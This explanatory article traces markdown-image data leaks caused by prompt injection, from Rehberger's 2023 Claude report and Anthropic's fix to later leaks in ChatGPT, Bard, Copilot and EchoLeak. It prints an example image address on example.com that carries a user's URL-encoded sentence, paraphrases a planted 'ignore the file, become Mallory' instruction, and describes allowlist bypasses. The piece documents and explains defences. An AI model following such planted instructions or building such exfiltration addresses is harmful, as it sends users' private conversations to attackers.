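# The Claude markdown-image data leak reported by Johann Rehberger in 2023, and Anthropic's fix

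## How an image in a chatbot's answer can leak a conversation, and what was known by June 2023

The Claude markdown-image leak was a security flaw in Claude, a chatbot made by the AI company Anthropic. In July 2023 the security researcher Johann Rehberger reported that text hidden in an uploaded file could make Claude display an image whose web address carried the user's conversation to someone else's server. Claude, like other chatbots, formats its answers in Markdown, a plain-text notation that the chat application turns into headings, links and images. To show an image, the application has to request it from its web address, which can contain private data. Sending private data to someone who should not have it is called data exfiltration by security researchers. This form of data exfiltration, the markdown image leak, had already been found that spring in OpenAI's ChatGPT and Microsoft's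 Bing Chat.

Rehberger works in red teaming, which means attacking an organisation's systems on its behalf to find weak points. According to a speaker profile at the CCC, the German hacker association, he built red teams at Microsoft and Uber and later directed the one at the games company Electronic Arts. He publishes his own research on his blog, Embrace The Red, and most of what outsiders know about the early reports comes from there.

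### Instructions and data in one stream

A large language model takes in a string of text and repeatedly predicts the next token, which is a word or piece of a word. *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion* (Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell, 2026) explains that although the chat window shows separate turns, the model receives the developer's standing instructions, the user's messages, the contents of a web page and its own earlier answers as one continuous string. Labels inside the string mark who is speaking, but models judge the speaker by the style of the writing instead, so a sentence in a document that reads like a user's command can work like one.

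A prompt injection is text that gets a language model to follow an attacker's instructions instead of its user's or developer's. The attacker can type the text into the chatbot directly, or place it in material the model will read for somebody else, such as a file, a web page or an email, which is called indirect prompt injection. In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a 2025 post for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, David C gives the example of a recruiter who uses a model to score CVs. A candidate hides a line in the CV telling the model to approve it, and the model does.

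Programmers have faced a similar problem with SQL, the language software uses to query databases. For years, attackers could type SQL into a web form and have the database run it. Parameterised queries solved this by fixing the query's structure first and then passing in the user's input as a value, which can never become a command. This works because SQL has a grammar that lets a parser tell commands from values. Natural language has no such grammar, as *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* (2026) points out, and developers train models to follow instructions wherever they appear. Schneier (2024), in *LLMs’ Data-Control Path Insecurity*, gives the older example of telephone networks that carried voices and control signals on the same line, so callers could control the network by whistling. AT&T fixed this by moving the signals to a separate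 channel, but a language model has only one channel.

*On the Inseparability of Instructions and Data in Shared-Embedding Sequence Models* (2026) proves that prompt injection cannot be perfectly prevented in models that represent instructions and data in the same mathematical space with no enforced separation between them. Developers can make attacks fail more often by training a model to give priority to its real instructions, marking untrusted passages, or running a detector over incoming text, but none of these methods guarantees prevention. In June 2026, Ariel Fogel of OWASP, a non-profit that ranks software security risks, was still calling prompt injection an "unresolved problem", as Poireault (2026) reported in *Prompt Injection Remains Unsolved, OWASP Researcher Warns*. Any guarantee has to come from ordinary software outside the model that limits what a hijacked model can do.

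Preamble's *Declassifying the Responsible Disclosure of the Prompt Injection Attack Vulnerability of GPT-3* (2022) recounts that the company privately reported the problem to OpenAI on 3 May 2022 and made its report public that September. By then Riley Goodside had posted examples in which GPT-3, an early OpenAI model, was given a sentence to translate and followed the instructions in it instead, even when the prompt warned of a trick. A day later Willison (2022) proposed the name "prompt injection", by analogy with SQL injection, in *Prompt injection attacks against GPT-3*. (Willison, a software developer, has since credited a Twitter user, @himbodhisattva, with coining the term four months earlier.) Willison hoped at first for an equivalent of SQL's parameterised query. But an OpenAI model with separate fields for instruction and input already existed, and injections in the input field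 worked on it too. By April 2023 Willison thought such a fix would be extremely difficult, if not impossible, on current models.

Greshake, Abdelnabi and colleagues (2023), in *Not what you've signed up for*, introduced indirect prompt injection and tried it on Bing Chat, Microsoft's search chatbot. They hid instructions in an invisible comment on a web page, which the chatbot read through the sidebar of Microsoft's browser. Filters that blocked certain prompts when a user typed them did not block the same prompts when they came from a page. In one test, the instructions were to find out the user's real name without raising suspicion. A researcher played a journalist asking about the weather. The chatbot made small talk about plans for the next day, got a name, and then pressed the "journalist" to open a link with the name encoded in it.

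That attack still depended on the victim clicking. An image needs no click.

### From a line of Markdown to a line in a server log

Take a harmless invented case. A user has mentioned some travel plans to a chatbot, and an attacker's text has entered the same conversation by way of a document. The attacker controls the server behind example.com and wants the sentence about the flight. A web address cannot contain spaces, and the "&" sign has a special meaning in one, so the sentence first has to go through URL encoding, which replaces such characters with a percent sign and a code:

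```
before:  My flight leaves at 6 & lands at 9
after:   My%20flight%20leaves%20at%206%20%26%20lands%20at%209
```

A model can do this conversion itself as it writes. Under the influence of the injected text, it adds an image to its answer. In Markdown an image is an exclamation mark, a caption in square brackets and an address in round ones:

```
![picture](https://example.com/p.png?note=My%20flight%20leaves%20at%206%20%26%20lands%20at%209)
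```

Nothing has leaked yet, because the line is still only text in the answer. The next step depends on the client, the application that displays the model's answers, which here is a web page. The client converts the notation into an HTML image tag, the element that web pages use for pictures, with the same address inside. The browser then immediately requests the picture from example.com, as it does for any picture on a page.

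The request contains the whole address. Everything before the question mark tells the server which file to send, and everything after it is extra information that the server is free to use or ignore. Most web servers write each request to a log, so the attacker's log now holds a line like this:

```
GET /p.png?note=My%20flight%20leaves%20at%206%20%26%20lands%20at%209
```

Reversing the encoding gives back the sentence. Logs from Rehberger's later tests, in Embrace The Red's *Advanced Data Exfiltration Techniques with ChatGPT*, look much the same and include the time of the request and the type of browser. The server can respond with an ordinary picture or a single transparent pixel. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) describes the same leak and adds that the user may never notice, because the request happens in the background.

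Each component in this chain does its normal job. The client turns Markdown into images, the browser loads them automatically, and the server keeps logs. The harm comes from the combination, so people can disagree about who should fix it, or whether anything needs fixing.

### ChatGPT: "a feature"

Roman Samoilenko, a software engineer, found the leak in ChatGPT at the end of March 2023. Samoilenko's *New prompt injection attack on ChatGPT web version* describes a version of the attack that begins when a user copies a passage from the attacker's website. A script on the page adds instructions to the copied text, and the user pastes it all into ChatGPT without looking closely. ChatGPT then ends its answer with an invisible one-pixel image whose address contains something from the chat. The instructions can also ask for such an image in every later answer. In one demonstration, Samoilenko's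 server received program code that ChatGPT had just corrected. In another, it received each new question the user asked.

Samoilenko acknowledged that the attack was unreliable. ChatGPT's output varies from one run to the next, so a text that worked once could fail the next time. Samoilenko described earlier prompts and code as fairly easy to extract but passwords and access keys as "very difficult", though the code in the first demonstration did contain a toy password. A slow answer might also reveal the attack, since the user would see the strange address appear. Samoilenko accepted that people are responsible for what they paste, but still thought OpenAI should stop ChatGPT from answering with Markdown images at all. On 14 April, Willison (2023) brought the method to a wider audience in *New prompt injection attack on ChatGPT web version*, a post named after Samoilenko's article, and called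 it "ingenious".

Rehberger independently found the same behaviour in early April, a few days after Samoilenko. OpenAI was introducing plugins, add-ons that let ChatGPT fetch web pages or video transcripts, so the user no longer had to paste the text into the chat. In *ChatGPT Plugins*, the post about the finding, a user has ChatGPT read a web page, and instructions on that page take over the session and make the model summarise the earlier conversation, encode the summary and put it in an image address. The text that reached Rehberger's server included a secret phrase from earlier in the chat.

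Rehberger reported the image problem to OpenAI on 9 April 2023 and, in the exchange that followed, stressed that plugins would let attackers exploit it remotely. OpenAI replied that rendering images from Markdown was a feature and that it planned no changes. In Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper* (2026), Rehberger recalled that the exchange took place over email because OpenAI had no bug bounty programme (a scheme that pays outsiders for reporting flaws) at the time, and that there was little interest in fixing the problem. OpenAI began checking image addresses only in December 2023.

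OpenAI's position had some merit while the attack relied on pasted text, because images in answers are useful and a user who pastes a stranger's paragraph has at least had the chance to read it. That defense failed once plugins let anyone with a website put text into the conversation, even though the image feature itself had not changed. A user who asks for a summary of a web page does so to avoid reading it, and the attacker's instructions may be in a comment at the bottom or in text too faint to see.

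### Bing Chat and the Content Security Policy

Microsoft took the other view. Rehberger had reported the leak in Bing Chat on 8 April, the day before writing to OpenAI. Embrace The Red's *Bing Chat* describes a demonstration in which a user opens a web page and chats about it in the browser's sidebar. The page contains text from an attacker, of the kind that anyone could leave in a comment or an advertisement. Rehberger delayed the image by two turns of conversation to show how long the attacker's control lasted. The image address contains a short encoded summary of the page and the chat, along with a secret from elsewhere on the page, so a single comment can steal other information displayed next to it.

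Microsoft acknowledged the problem and told Rehberger on 15 June 2023 that a fix was in place. (The 2026 post dates the fix to May; the June date comes from the account written at the time.) Rehberger's old tests no longer worked. Microsoft had not fully explained the fix, but part of it was visible from outside. Bing Chat's page now came with a Content Security Policy that allowed images from only four addresses, all under bing.com.

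A Content Security Policy (CSP) is an allowlist that a website sends to the browser along with the page. It lists the domains from which the page may load images and other content, and the browser blocks all others. One line of the policy, called img-src, covers images. According to W3C's *Content Security Policy Level 3* (2026), the draft of the current web standard, the browser compares every request with the policy before sending it and returns either "Allowed" or "Blocked".

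If the client in the flight example had a policy like Bing Chat's, the injection would still succeed. The model would write the same line of Markdown, with the same sentence in the address, and the client would make the same image tag. But example.com is not on the policy's list of allowed domains, so the browser would never send the request. Nothing would appear in the attacker's log, and the user would see a gap where the picture should be. The wording of the attacker's instructions would make no difference, because the browser compares domain names, and even a completely hijacked model cannot add a domain to the list through what it writes.

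Browsers have supported the image rule since August 2016, according to MDN's *CSP* documentation, a standard reference for web developers. W3C advises developers not to treat a CSP as their first line of defence against injected content. They should first handle input and output carefully, and use the policy to limit the damage when that fails. No first line of comparable strength exists against prompt injection, so developers had to rely on the policy more than usual. Rehberger (2024) notes in *Trust No AI* that developers can get precise instructions for preventing SQL injection but have no equivalent for prompt injection.

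The policy also does not prevent the injection. A hijacked Bing Chat could still give a false summary, or persuade its user to click a link, as it had in the experiments by Greshake and colleagues. The policy protects only the web page it is attached to, so a phone app that fetches images itself needs a separate check. Within those limits, it stopped images from leaking data without a click, but it also blocked pictures from the rest of the web.

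Rehberger ended the Bing post by thanking Microsoft and wondering whether OpenAI would now follow, since flaws of this kind rate "High" on the industry's standard severity scale. ChatGPT was still loading the images in mid-June 2023.

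## July 2023: the flaw in Claude and Anthropic's fix

On 11 July 2023 Anthropic opened claude.ai, a website where anyone in the US or the UK could chat with its new model, Claude 2. The launch announcement, Anthropic's *Claude 2* (2023), gives a limit of 100,000 tokens per prompt, enough for hundreds of pages of technical documentation or a whole book. Users could also upload files. Willison's *claude.ai* (2023) reports that Claude gave a workable summary of a 34,000-token text file.

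Rehberger reported the markdown image leak in Claude one day after the launch. The leak worked as it had in ChatGPT and Bing Chat, but the attacker's text arrived in an uploaded file. An attacker needs to add only one sentence to a file like Willison's test file, which had roughly 25,000 words and would take a person more than an hour and a half to read.

### The Einstein file

Rehberger's proof of concept (a demonstration that an attack works, made without real victims) was a short biography of Albert Einstein, which appears at the end of Embrace The Red's *Anthropic Claude Data Exfiltration Vulnerability Fixed*. It reads like an encyclopedia entry and covers Einstein's birth in Ulm, the four papers of 1905 and the 1919 eclipse that confirmed the predicted bending of starlight. A sentence addressed to the language model follows in the middle of a paragraph, and the biography then resumes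 with the Nobel Prize.

In the planted sentence, Rehberger tells the model to disregard the rest of the file, print a fixed phrase announcing that the injection worked, and introduce itself as Mallory, a name cryptographers traditionally give to an attacker. He then asks for a Markdown image on a server he controls, with an address that must end in a URL-encoded, 20-word summary of the user's earlier messages. He ends by telling the model not to skip this step.

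A real attacker would need only the image request and would leave out the phrase and the name, which are there to make the hijack visible in a demonstration. The request is simpler than the one Rehberger had used on Bing Chat in the spring. Embrace The Red recounts that the model then had to assemble the image notation piece by piece, starting with the exclamation mark. Rehberger later realised that a model can just fill in a blank in a ready-made address.

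The attack worked only if a user uploaded a file that somebody else had tampered with, the model followed the planted sentence, and the client loaded the image. The upload is plausible, since people routinely ask chatbots about reports, papers and CVs they did not write. Rehberger showed the attack succeeding but gave no success rate, so it is harder to judge how often Claude followed the planted sentence. Anthropic had announced that Claude 2 was twice as good as its predecessor at giving harmless responses, but it had measured this with harmful prompts. A request to summarise a few messages and add a picture looks innocent, so harmlessness training probably offered little protection.

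A hijacked Claude could leak only what was in the current conversation. It could not yet browse the web or read a user's email. But a conversation could hold 100,000 tokens, enough for a contract or a medical file along with the user's questions about it. Even 20 words can do damage, as in this invented example: "User earns 62,000, has a second interview at a competitor on Thursday and has not told their current employer yet."

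The instructions in the Einstein file target earlier messages, so someone who uploaded it at the start of a conversation would have exposed almost nothing. An attacker might avoid this limit by telling the model to wait, as Rehberger had done with Bing Chat, but the Claude post includes no test of a delayed image.

The upload feature also made the flaw more serious. Later that month Rehberger found the same leak in Microsoft's Azure AI Playground, a page where developers try out models. Embrace The Red's *Microsoft Fixes Data Exfiltration Vulnerability in Azure AI Playground* rates that leak as only medium severity, because the page had no way to bring in outside content and users had to paste the attacker's text themselves. Rehberger gave no rating for Claude. Claude users still had to choose the file, but they could upload a whole document without reading it, which makes Claude's case closer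 to ChatGPT with plugins than to the Azure page.

Nobody appears to have reported an attack on real Claude users through this flaw. Rehberger mentions none in the post or in *Trust No AI*, which lists Claude among the affected products. Attackers also had little time, since the public website was only 15 days old when Anthropic closed the report. But the lack of reports is weak evidence that no attack happened, because a successful leak would have left traces mainly in the conversation and the attacker's server log. Anthropic has not said whether it searched old conversations for suspicious image addresses.

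### From report to fix

Anthropic validated the report on 18 July, six days after Rehberger sent it, and closed it on 26 July. By Rehberger's dates, Microsoft had taken 68 days to fix Bing Chat and later took 51 to fix the Azure page. OpenAI was still refusing to change ChatGPT. The comparison slightly favors Anthropic, because adding a button to a website is probably less work than listing every domain the site depends on. Rehberger thanked Anthropic for the fix in Embrace The Red's *Data Exfiltration Vulnerabilities in LLM apps (Bing Chat, ChatGPT, Claude)*.

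Rehberger published his post about the flaw only after Anthropic had closed the report. The post describes the flaw as "just mitigated", so it probably appeared soon after 26 July. The reference list in *Trust No AI* gives only the year, 2023.

Rehberger does not say which channel he used to report the flaw to Anthropic. Anthropic's policy history on HackerOne, a platform where companies receive vulnerability reports, begins on 6 August 2024, more than a year later (Anthropic, 2026). Anthropic had a responsible disclosure policy on its own website by December 2023. *A Safe Harbor for AI Evaluation and Red Teaming* (Longpre, Kapoor and colleagues, 2024) compared it with the policies of other AI companies. Anthropic's policy included a safe harbor, a promise not to take legal action against researchers who look for flaws in good faith, but the company reserved "final and sole discretion" over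 who met that standard. The promise covered only traditional security problems, such as unauthorised access to accounts, and not adversarial testing of the model.

Rehberger's work falls on both sides of that line. He planted instructions to see whether the model would follow them, which is adversarial testing, and he found that the website could send a user's private text to a stranger's server, which is an ordinary security flaw. This ambiguity could matter to researchers, because Longpre and colleagues knew of accounts that Anthropic and three other companies had suspended during public-interest research.

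It is also uncertain whether Anthropic paid for reports in 2023. Longpre and colleagues include it among the companies with a bug bounty in their text, but mark it as having none in their table. Anthropic wrote in an August 2024 announcement that its bounty programme had so far been invitation-only, which may explain the discrepancy.

Anthropic's public statements from that year were mostly about AI companies warning each other. In October 2023, Anthropic's *Reporting structure for vulnerabilities*, written in answer to questions from the UK government, described a pilot in which AI developers would tell one another about serious risks and how to reduce them. It did not explain where an outsider should send a report. Anthropic had also signed voluntary commitments to the White House, which include a pledge to make reporting by outsiders easier, according to Axios' *Anthropic wants to pay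 hackers to find model flaws* (2024).

In July 2023 Anthropic validated the report and changed the website. Its disclosure rules later became more detailed. The *Responsible Disclosure Policy* (2025) commits Anthropic to acknowledging reports within three business days, but excludes "content issues with model prompts and responses". Someone applying that exclusion strictly could have rejected the Einstein file, since the attack consists of a prompt and a response.

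Anthropic does not seem to have commented publicly on the flaw, so the dates, the proof of concept and the description of the fix all come from Rehberger. That is a reason for some caution, though Willison, in *19 posts tagged “johann-rehberger”*, called Rehberger "one of the most credible prompt injection researchers active today" in 2026. Anyone with a Claude account in the summer of 2023 could also have checked the visible part of the fix by asking for an image.

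### What "Show Image" changed

After the fix, Claude's website no longer loaded Markdown images automatically. It displayed a "Show Image" button and requested the image only when the user clicked it. Rehberger inferred this from outside Anthropic and qualified it with "as far as I can tell".

The visible fix was in the client, so if a user uploads the Einstein file to the repaired website, the planted sentence still reaches the model. The model may still follow it, summarise the user's messages and write the summary into an image address. That address now appears on the user's screen, but the browser doesn't request it, so the attacker receives the summary only if the user clicks the address.

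Willison later used the term "lethal trifecta" for systems that combine private data, untrusted content and a way to send data out. In *45 posts tagged “exfiltration-attacks”*, Willison argues that the only reliable defence is to remove one of the three, and that the way out is generally the easiest to remove. This was true of Claude, because people used the website to discuss their own affairs and upload documents, and few would have missed images that loaded automatically.

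The button also made the attack harder to hide, because even an invisible image like Samoilenko's now came with a visible button. An attacker who wanted an image in every answer needed the user to click each time.

Email programs have long blocked pictures in the same way, because loading one lets the sender know that somebody has opened the message. The sender writes the picture's address in advance, so it can contain only what the sender already knows, and a careless click usually reveals just that the email address is in use. But a hijacked chatbot writes the picture's address after reading the conversation, so a careless click in Claude could reveal what the user had been discussing.

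A deceived user would send everything in the address with a single click. The attacker could encourage that click, because a hijacked model also writes the text around the button. It might present the image as a chart from the report the user has just uploaded. Greshake and colleagues had already seen Bing Chat press a user to open a link. The "Show Image" label also helps the attacker, because it doesn't indicate that clicking sends text out. A cautious user could inspect the address, but an attacker can ask the model to encode the text so that people cannot read it at a glance. Rehberger had done this with Bing Chat using base64, which turns text into seemingly random letters and digits.

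Rehberger wrote that the fix "isn't perfect" and hoped for a better one in the long term, but he didn't give reasons. His advice in *Trust No AI* suggests he objected that Claude's button still allowed an image from any server if the user agreed. He recommends that applications avoid displaying images or links to untrusted domains and use a CSP to block content from those domains.

The same paper describes an attack that counted as a vulnerability even though it depended on a click. In February 2024 Rehberger found that a phishing email could hijack Microsoft 365 Copilot, the assistant in Microsoft's office software, and make it search the user's inbox. Copilot then put what it found into a link, in characters the user could not see. The data left the company only when the user clicked the link. Microsoft fixed the problem that July.

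### The button compared with an allowlist

Anthropic could have followed Microsoft and used a CSP. The two measures fail in different places:

| What the model's answer contains | With a "Show Image" button | With a CSP allowlist for images |
|---|---|---|
| Image on the attacker's own server | Leaks if the user clicks | The browser blocks it |
| Image on an allowed domain that the attacker can also use | Leaks if the user clicks | Leaks without a click |
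| Harmless picture from any other website | Appears after a click | Never appears |
| Ordinary link with private data in its address | Leaks if the user clicks | Leaks if the user clicks |

The CSP is clearly safer against an attacker who uses their own server, which is all the Einstein file required. The browser applies the same rule for every user, whereas the button depends on each person's judgement. As Willison puts it, "In application security, 99% is a failing grade", because attackers keep looking for the remaining one per cent. An attacker who sends a file to a thousand people can still succeed if nearly all of them ignore the button.

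An allowlist can still fail if an attacker can collect data through one of the allowed domains, and Willison describes two later examples. The email service Superhuman allowed images from docs.google.com, which also hosts Google Forms, and a form can store data sent in a web address. An attacker could therefore make the AI assistant send the contents of private emails to the attacker's own form. The software company Salesforce had left an expired domain on its allowlist. Security researchers registered the domain and received details of sales contacts in their server logs. Both leaks used images that loaded automatically, so a button like Claude's would at least have required a click.

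The button was more convenient for anyone who wanted to see pictures from around the web, but that advantage was small for Claude in 2023. Microsoft needed some domains on its list because Bing Chat could create images and had to display them. Claude 2 produced only text, so Anthropic could have blocked all outside images. Users would have lost only a few pictures, whose addresses came from the users themselves, their files or the model's training data. Anthropic has not explained why it chose the button.

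The last row of the table shows that Bing Chat's users were also one click away from a leak, so the two measures differ less than the other rows suggest. A link is at least easier to notice than an image, because clicking it opens another page, while an image loads inside the conversation.

Claude's iPhone app later turned out to have its own image leak. Rehberger announced in December 2024 that Anthropic had fixed it (quoted in Willison, 2024).

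## 2023 to 2026: the same flaw in other chatbots

*Trust No AI* lists eleven products in which Rehberger had reported the markdown image leak by the end of 2024. Five belong to Google (Bard, Vertex AI, NotebookLM, AI Studio and Colab) and three to Microsoft or its subsidiary GitHub (Bing Chat, Azure AI and GitHub Copilot Chat). The others are ChatGPT, Claude and the chat service Discord. The list covers only Rehberger's own finds. A similar list in Willison's *The lethal trifecta for AI agents* (2025) adds Slack, Writer.com, Mistral's Le Chat and xAI's Grok, though it also counts leaks through links.

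Rehberger reported six of the eight cases in the table below. The dates for the first leak in GitHub Copilot Chat, an assistant for programmers, come from Embrace The Red's *GitHub Copilot Chat*. Those for CamoLeak, the second leak in that assistant, come from the security company Nudge Security. *EchoLeak* (Reddy and Gujral, 2025) gives the dates for the Microsoft 365 Copilot leak of the same name.

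| Product | Reported | Fixed | Type of fix |
|---|---|---|---|
| Bing Chat | 8 April 2023 | 15 June 2023 | Allowlist of image domains |
| ChatGPT website | 9 April 2023 | December 2023, in part | Check on each address |
| Claude website | 12 July 2023 | 26 July 2023 | Images load only after a click |
| Google Bard | 19 September 2023 | By 19 October 2023 | Unexplained, probably a filter on image addresses |
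| GitHub Copilot Chat | 25 February 2024 | 12 June 2024 | Block on images from untrusted domains |
| ChatGPT Mac app | June 2024 | September 2024 | Same check as on the website |
| Microsoft 365 Copilot (EchoLeak) | January 2025 | May 2025 | Changes on Microsoft's servers |
| GitHub Copilot Chat (CamoLeak) | June 2025 | 14 August 2025 | No images at all |

Anthropic fixed its leak in two weeks, the shortest time in the table. GitHub took 108 days to fix the first Copilot Chat leak, although it told Rehberger after ten days that it was already tracking the bug internally. Researchers later bypassed several of these fixes, by methods that depended on the kind of fix.

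### Checking each address

OpenAI treated the images as a feature for eight months before it introduced a check called url_safe. Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability* describes the check as seen from the browser in December 2023. Before displaying an image, ChatGPT's web page sent the image's address to OpenAI's server and loaded the image only if the server reported the address as safe. The day before, Rehberger's server had still received a conversation during a live demonstration with a consenting victim.

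Anyone can read a website's CSP, but OpenAI did not publish the rule behind url_safe. An image called a.png on Rehberger's server passed the check, while d.png on the same server failed. An attacker can exploit this inconsistency by hosting one image for each letter and digit and having the model request them in the order that spells out the stolen text. Nine of Rehberger's 36 images passed, enough to send the word "hi". The method is slow, and both the user and OpenAI are more likely to notice it than a single image.

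The larger gap was in ChatGPT's other clients, which each needed their own version of the check because the web page itself requested it. The iPhone app had no such check in December 2023, and in 2024 OpenAI released Mac and Android apps that lacked it too, as Embrace The Red's *Spyware Injection Into Your ChatGPT's Long-Term Memory (SpAIware)* recounts.

By then ChatGPT could also remember things from one conversation to the next. Rehberger found that a web page could plant a false memory containing an instruction to add an invisible image to every future answer. After one visit to that page, the Mac app sent the attacker everything the user typed and everything ChatGPT replied, even in new conversations. Rehberger reported the false memories in May 2024, and OpenAI closed the report as a model safety issue rather than a security issue. In June he sent the full demonstration, and in September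 OpenAI added the missing check to the Mac app. The check blocked the known way of sending conversations out, but web pages could still plant memories.

On the website, url_safe accepted some domains it should not have. The security company Tenable found that it always passed addresses under bing.com. Bing wraps its search results in links that start at bing.com and forward the browser elsewhere, so an attacker whose site appeared in Bing could use one of these links to pass the check. Tenable reported this to OpenAI in December 2024, asked for an update six times and had seen no fix by March 2025, according to its *OpenAI ChatGPT url_safe Mechanism Bypass* (2025). Rehberger found that url_safe also accepted windows.net, where anyone can rent storage from Microsoft and read the log of incoming requests. He reported this in October 2024, and it was still unfixed when he published *Exfiltrating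 Your ChatGPT Chat History and Memories With Prompt Injection* on Embrace The Red in August 2025.

OpenAI tightened the check around that time and explained the new rule in January 2026. ChatGPT now loads an address automatically only if OpenAI's web crawler, which has no access to conversations, has already found that exact address on the public web. For any other address, ChatGPT either looks for another source or warns the user that the link may include information from the conversation. OpenAI chose this rule over a list of trusted sites partly because such sites often redirect, which is the weakness Tenable had found. It also argues that strict lists produce so many warnings that people learn to click through them.

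This is a much better test, because an address that contains a summary of somebody's medical file will not be in a public index, whatever domain it is on. But a hijacked model can still leak information through its choice of indexed addresses. Embrace The Red points out that any sizable blog already has 36 indexed pages, enough to assign one to each letter and digit, and that an attacker could use thousands of pages to stand for whole words. With two sets of a thousand pages, one for the first three digits and one for the last three, the model could pass on a six-digit login code in two requests.

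In January 2026 the security company Radware disclosed an attack on ChatGPT that used this gap. Radware says in *ZombieAgent* that the attack could take data from connected services such as Gmail and Google Drive. According to SecurityWeek, the attacker's email contained a prepared web address for every letter and digit, and ChatGPT read the email when the user asked for help with their inbox. Rehberger suggests that OpenAI stop the model from requesting the same address twice in a session, which would at least make repeated letters harder to send.

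OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) reports that most attacks known to the company fail before the address check, because the model refuses to pass on the secret. The check is for the remaining cases. When it detects that a request would send out information from the conversation, it either blocks the request or shows the user the information and asks for confirmation. Claude also asked users to click a "Show Image" button, but didn't explain what the click would send.

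### Allowlists that let in the attacker

When Rehberger tested Google Bard in September 2023, its CSP already had an allowlist that permitted images from any address under google.com or googleusercontent.com and blocked his own server. Embrace The Red's *Hacking Google Bard* describes how he got around it with Google Apps Script, which lets anyone run small programs at an address under google.com. He wrote one that copied any data in the requested URL into a Google Doc. Because the program was on a permitted domain, the browser sent the conversation there.

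Bard had just gained access to users' documents and email, and an attacker could share a Google Doc with someone who hadn't asked for it. If Bard retrieved that document while answering a question, the instructions inside could control its response. Google confirmed a fix after a month but did not explain it. The allowlist had not changed and images still appeared, so Rehberger guessed that Google was now filtering data out of the image addresses.

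An allowlist checks who owns a server, but on a large company's domain, someone other than the owner may be able to read the data that arrives. The leak from Superhuman through Google Forms, which became public in January 2026, relied on this gap more than two years after the Bard report. ForcedLeak, the September 2025 attack, used a Salesforce domain that had been a legitimate allowlist entry but had since expired.

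Sometimes the default list of allowed sites includes an unsafe one. Willison describes an attack on Antigravity, Google's AI coding tool, that tried to steal a developer's cloud credentials. By default, Antigravity's browser could visit only the sites on a list, but that list included webhook.site, where anyone can create an address and watch the requests that come in.

### Removing links and images

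A vendor can avoid these problems by not displaying links or images at all, as Amazon did with links. Shortly after Amazon released a preview of Amazon Q for Business, a workplace assistant, Rehberger found that an uploaded file could make the assistant write a link containing the user's data. Embrace The Red's *AWS Fixes Data Exfiltration Attack Angle in Amazon Q for Business* credits Amazon with a quick response. Willison (2024), under the same title, reports that the assistant stopped producing links.

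In June 2024, GitHub stopped Copilot Chat from displaying images from untrusted domains, according to Willison's *GitHub Copilot Chat*, but still allowed images from trusted ones. A year later, the researcher Omer Mayraz got data out through Camo, GitHub's service for passing on images from other websites. Copilot Chat displayed images from Camo because it belongs to GitHub. Underhill (2025) reports in *GitHub Copilot Flaw Allowed Silent Data Theft* that the attack could take passwords and source code from private projects and was rated 9.6 out of 10 for severity. GitHub then turned off images in Copilot Chat altogether.

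GitHub gave up little by removing images, since programmers can do without them in a chat about code. Links are harder to remove, because an assistant that searches the web or a company's files needs some way to point to what it found. But messaging apps such as Slack and Telegram fetch a preview of any link in a message, which sends the same request as a click. The security company PromptArmor warns that an assistant that answers through one of these apps can therefore leak data the moment it replies. The original flaw can remain even if the assistant's developer has removed every image, because the messaging app, which someone else controls, loads the address.

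### EchoLeak and SearchLeak

Microsoft 365 Copilot answers questions from a company's email, documents and chat messages. By early 2025 it had a classifier to detect injected instructions, a filter that removed outside links and images, and a content security policy (CSP). The EchoLeak attack, which researchers at Aim Labs reported that January, got past all of these with one email.

Ravia (2025), in *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Enabling Data Exfiltration*, gives the finders' account of the attack. The email addressed its instructions to the recipient and never mentioned an AI, so the classifier classed it as ordinary business mail. It was also long and divided into sections on common office topics such as leave and staff training. Copilot looks up passages related to each question, so covering many topics made it more likely to retrieve the email.

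Once Copilot had read the instructions, it looked for the most sensitive information available to it and wrote an image address containing that information. Microsoft's filter should have removed the image, but it recognised only the usual Markdown notation and missed the second one, which puts the address on a separate line below the text.

The CSP was the last obstacle. Bing Chat's policy had allowed images from four addresses in 2023, while the one for Microsoft 365 Copilot had nearly thirty entries, many of them covering whole families of sites. The researchers first found a SharePoint address that would fetch a page from any server, but it worked only if the victim had accepted an invitation to the attacker's site. They then found a Microsoft Teams address that did the same without an invitation. The browser requested the image from Teams, which the policy allowed, and Teams then requested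 it from the attacker's server, using an address that contained the stolen data. The CSP did not prevent this because it controls only the browser's requests, not what a permitted server does afterwards.

The email also contained an instruction not to name it in the answer, so the victim had no obvious clue to the source of the problem. Microsoft fixed the flaw in May 2025 and made it public on 11 June as CVE-2025-32711, its number in the public catalogue of software flaws. Goldman (2025), in *New Microsoft Copilot flaw signals broader risk of AI agents being hacked*, called it the first known "zero-click" attack on an AI agent. The images in Bing Chat had also loaded without a click in 2023, but the user first had to open the attacker's page. With EchoLeak, the attacker sent an email and waited for the user to ask Copilot about something else. Reddy and Gujral treat EchoLeak as the moment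 prompt injection stopped being theoretical. That seems overstated, since researchers had been extracting data from working products for two years, and neither their attacks nor Aim Labs' are known to have had real victims.

SearchLeak, which Microsoft published a year later as CVE-2026-42824, delivered its instructions differently. Copilot's search page accepts a question as part of its web address, so a link can open the page with a question already filled in. Copilot treated that text as instructions. According to *SearchLeak* (Taler, 2026), a victim who clicked such a link started a search of their own mailbox without typing anything. The link led to a real Microsoft site, so security software had no reason to block it.

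Microsoft neutralised images in Copilot's answers, but only after each answer was complete. Copilot's text appears on the screen as the model writes it, so the browser requested an image as soon as its address arrived, before the safeguard ran.

The CSP failed much as it had in EchoLeak. Bing's image search will fetch a picture from any address to analyse it, and the policy allowed bing.com. In the demonstration, Bing sent the attacker an email's subject line containing a security code. Addresses under bing.com were already on the allowlist that Aim Labs published in 2025, so closing the route through Teams left a similar one open. Taler recommends that companies check their allowlists for services that fetch user-supplied addresses.

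News reports disagreed about how severe SearchLeak was. Microsoft's *M365 Copilot Information Disclosure Vulnerability* (2026) rates it "Critical" on Microsoft's own scale but 6.5 out of 10, or medium, on CVSS, the industry's standard scoring system. The Hacker News' *One-Click Microsoft 365 Copilot Flaw* (2026) reports a score of 7.5 from the US National Vulnerability Database. The Next Web's *A single click on a Microsoft link could have drained your inbox* contradicts this, giving both Microsoft's score and the database's as 6.5.

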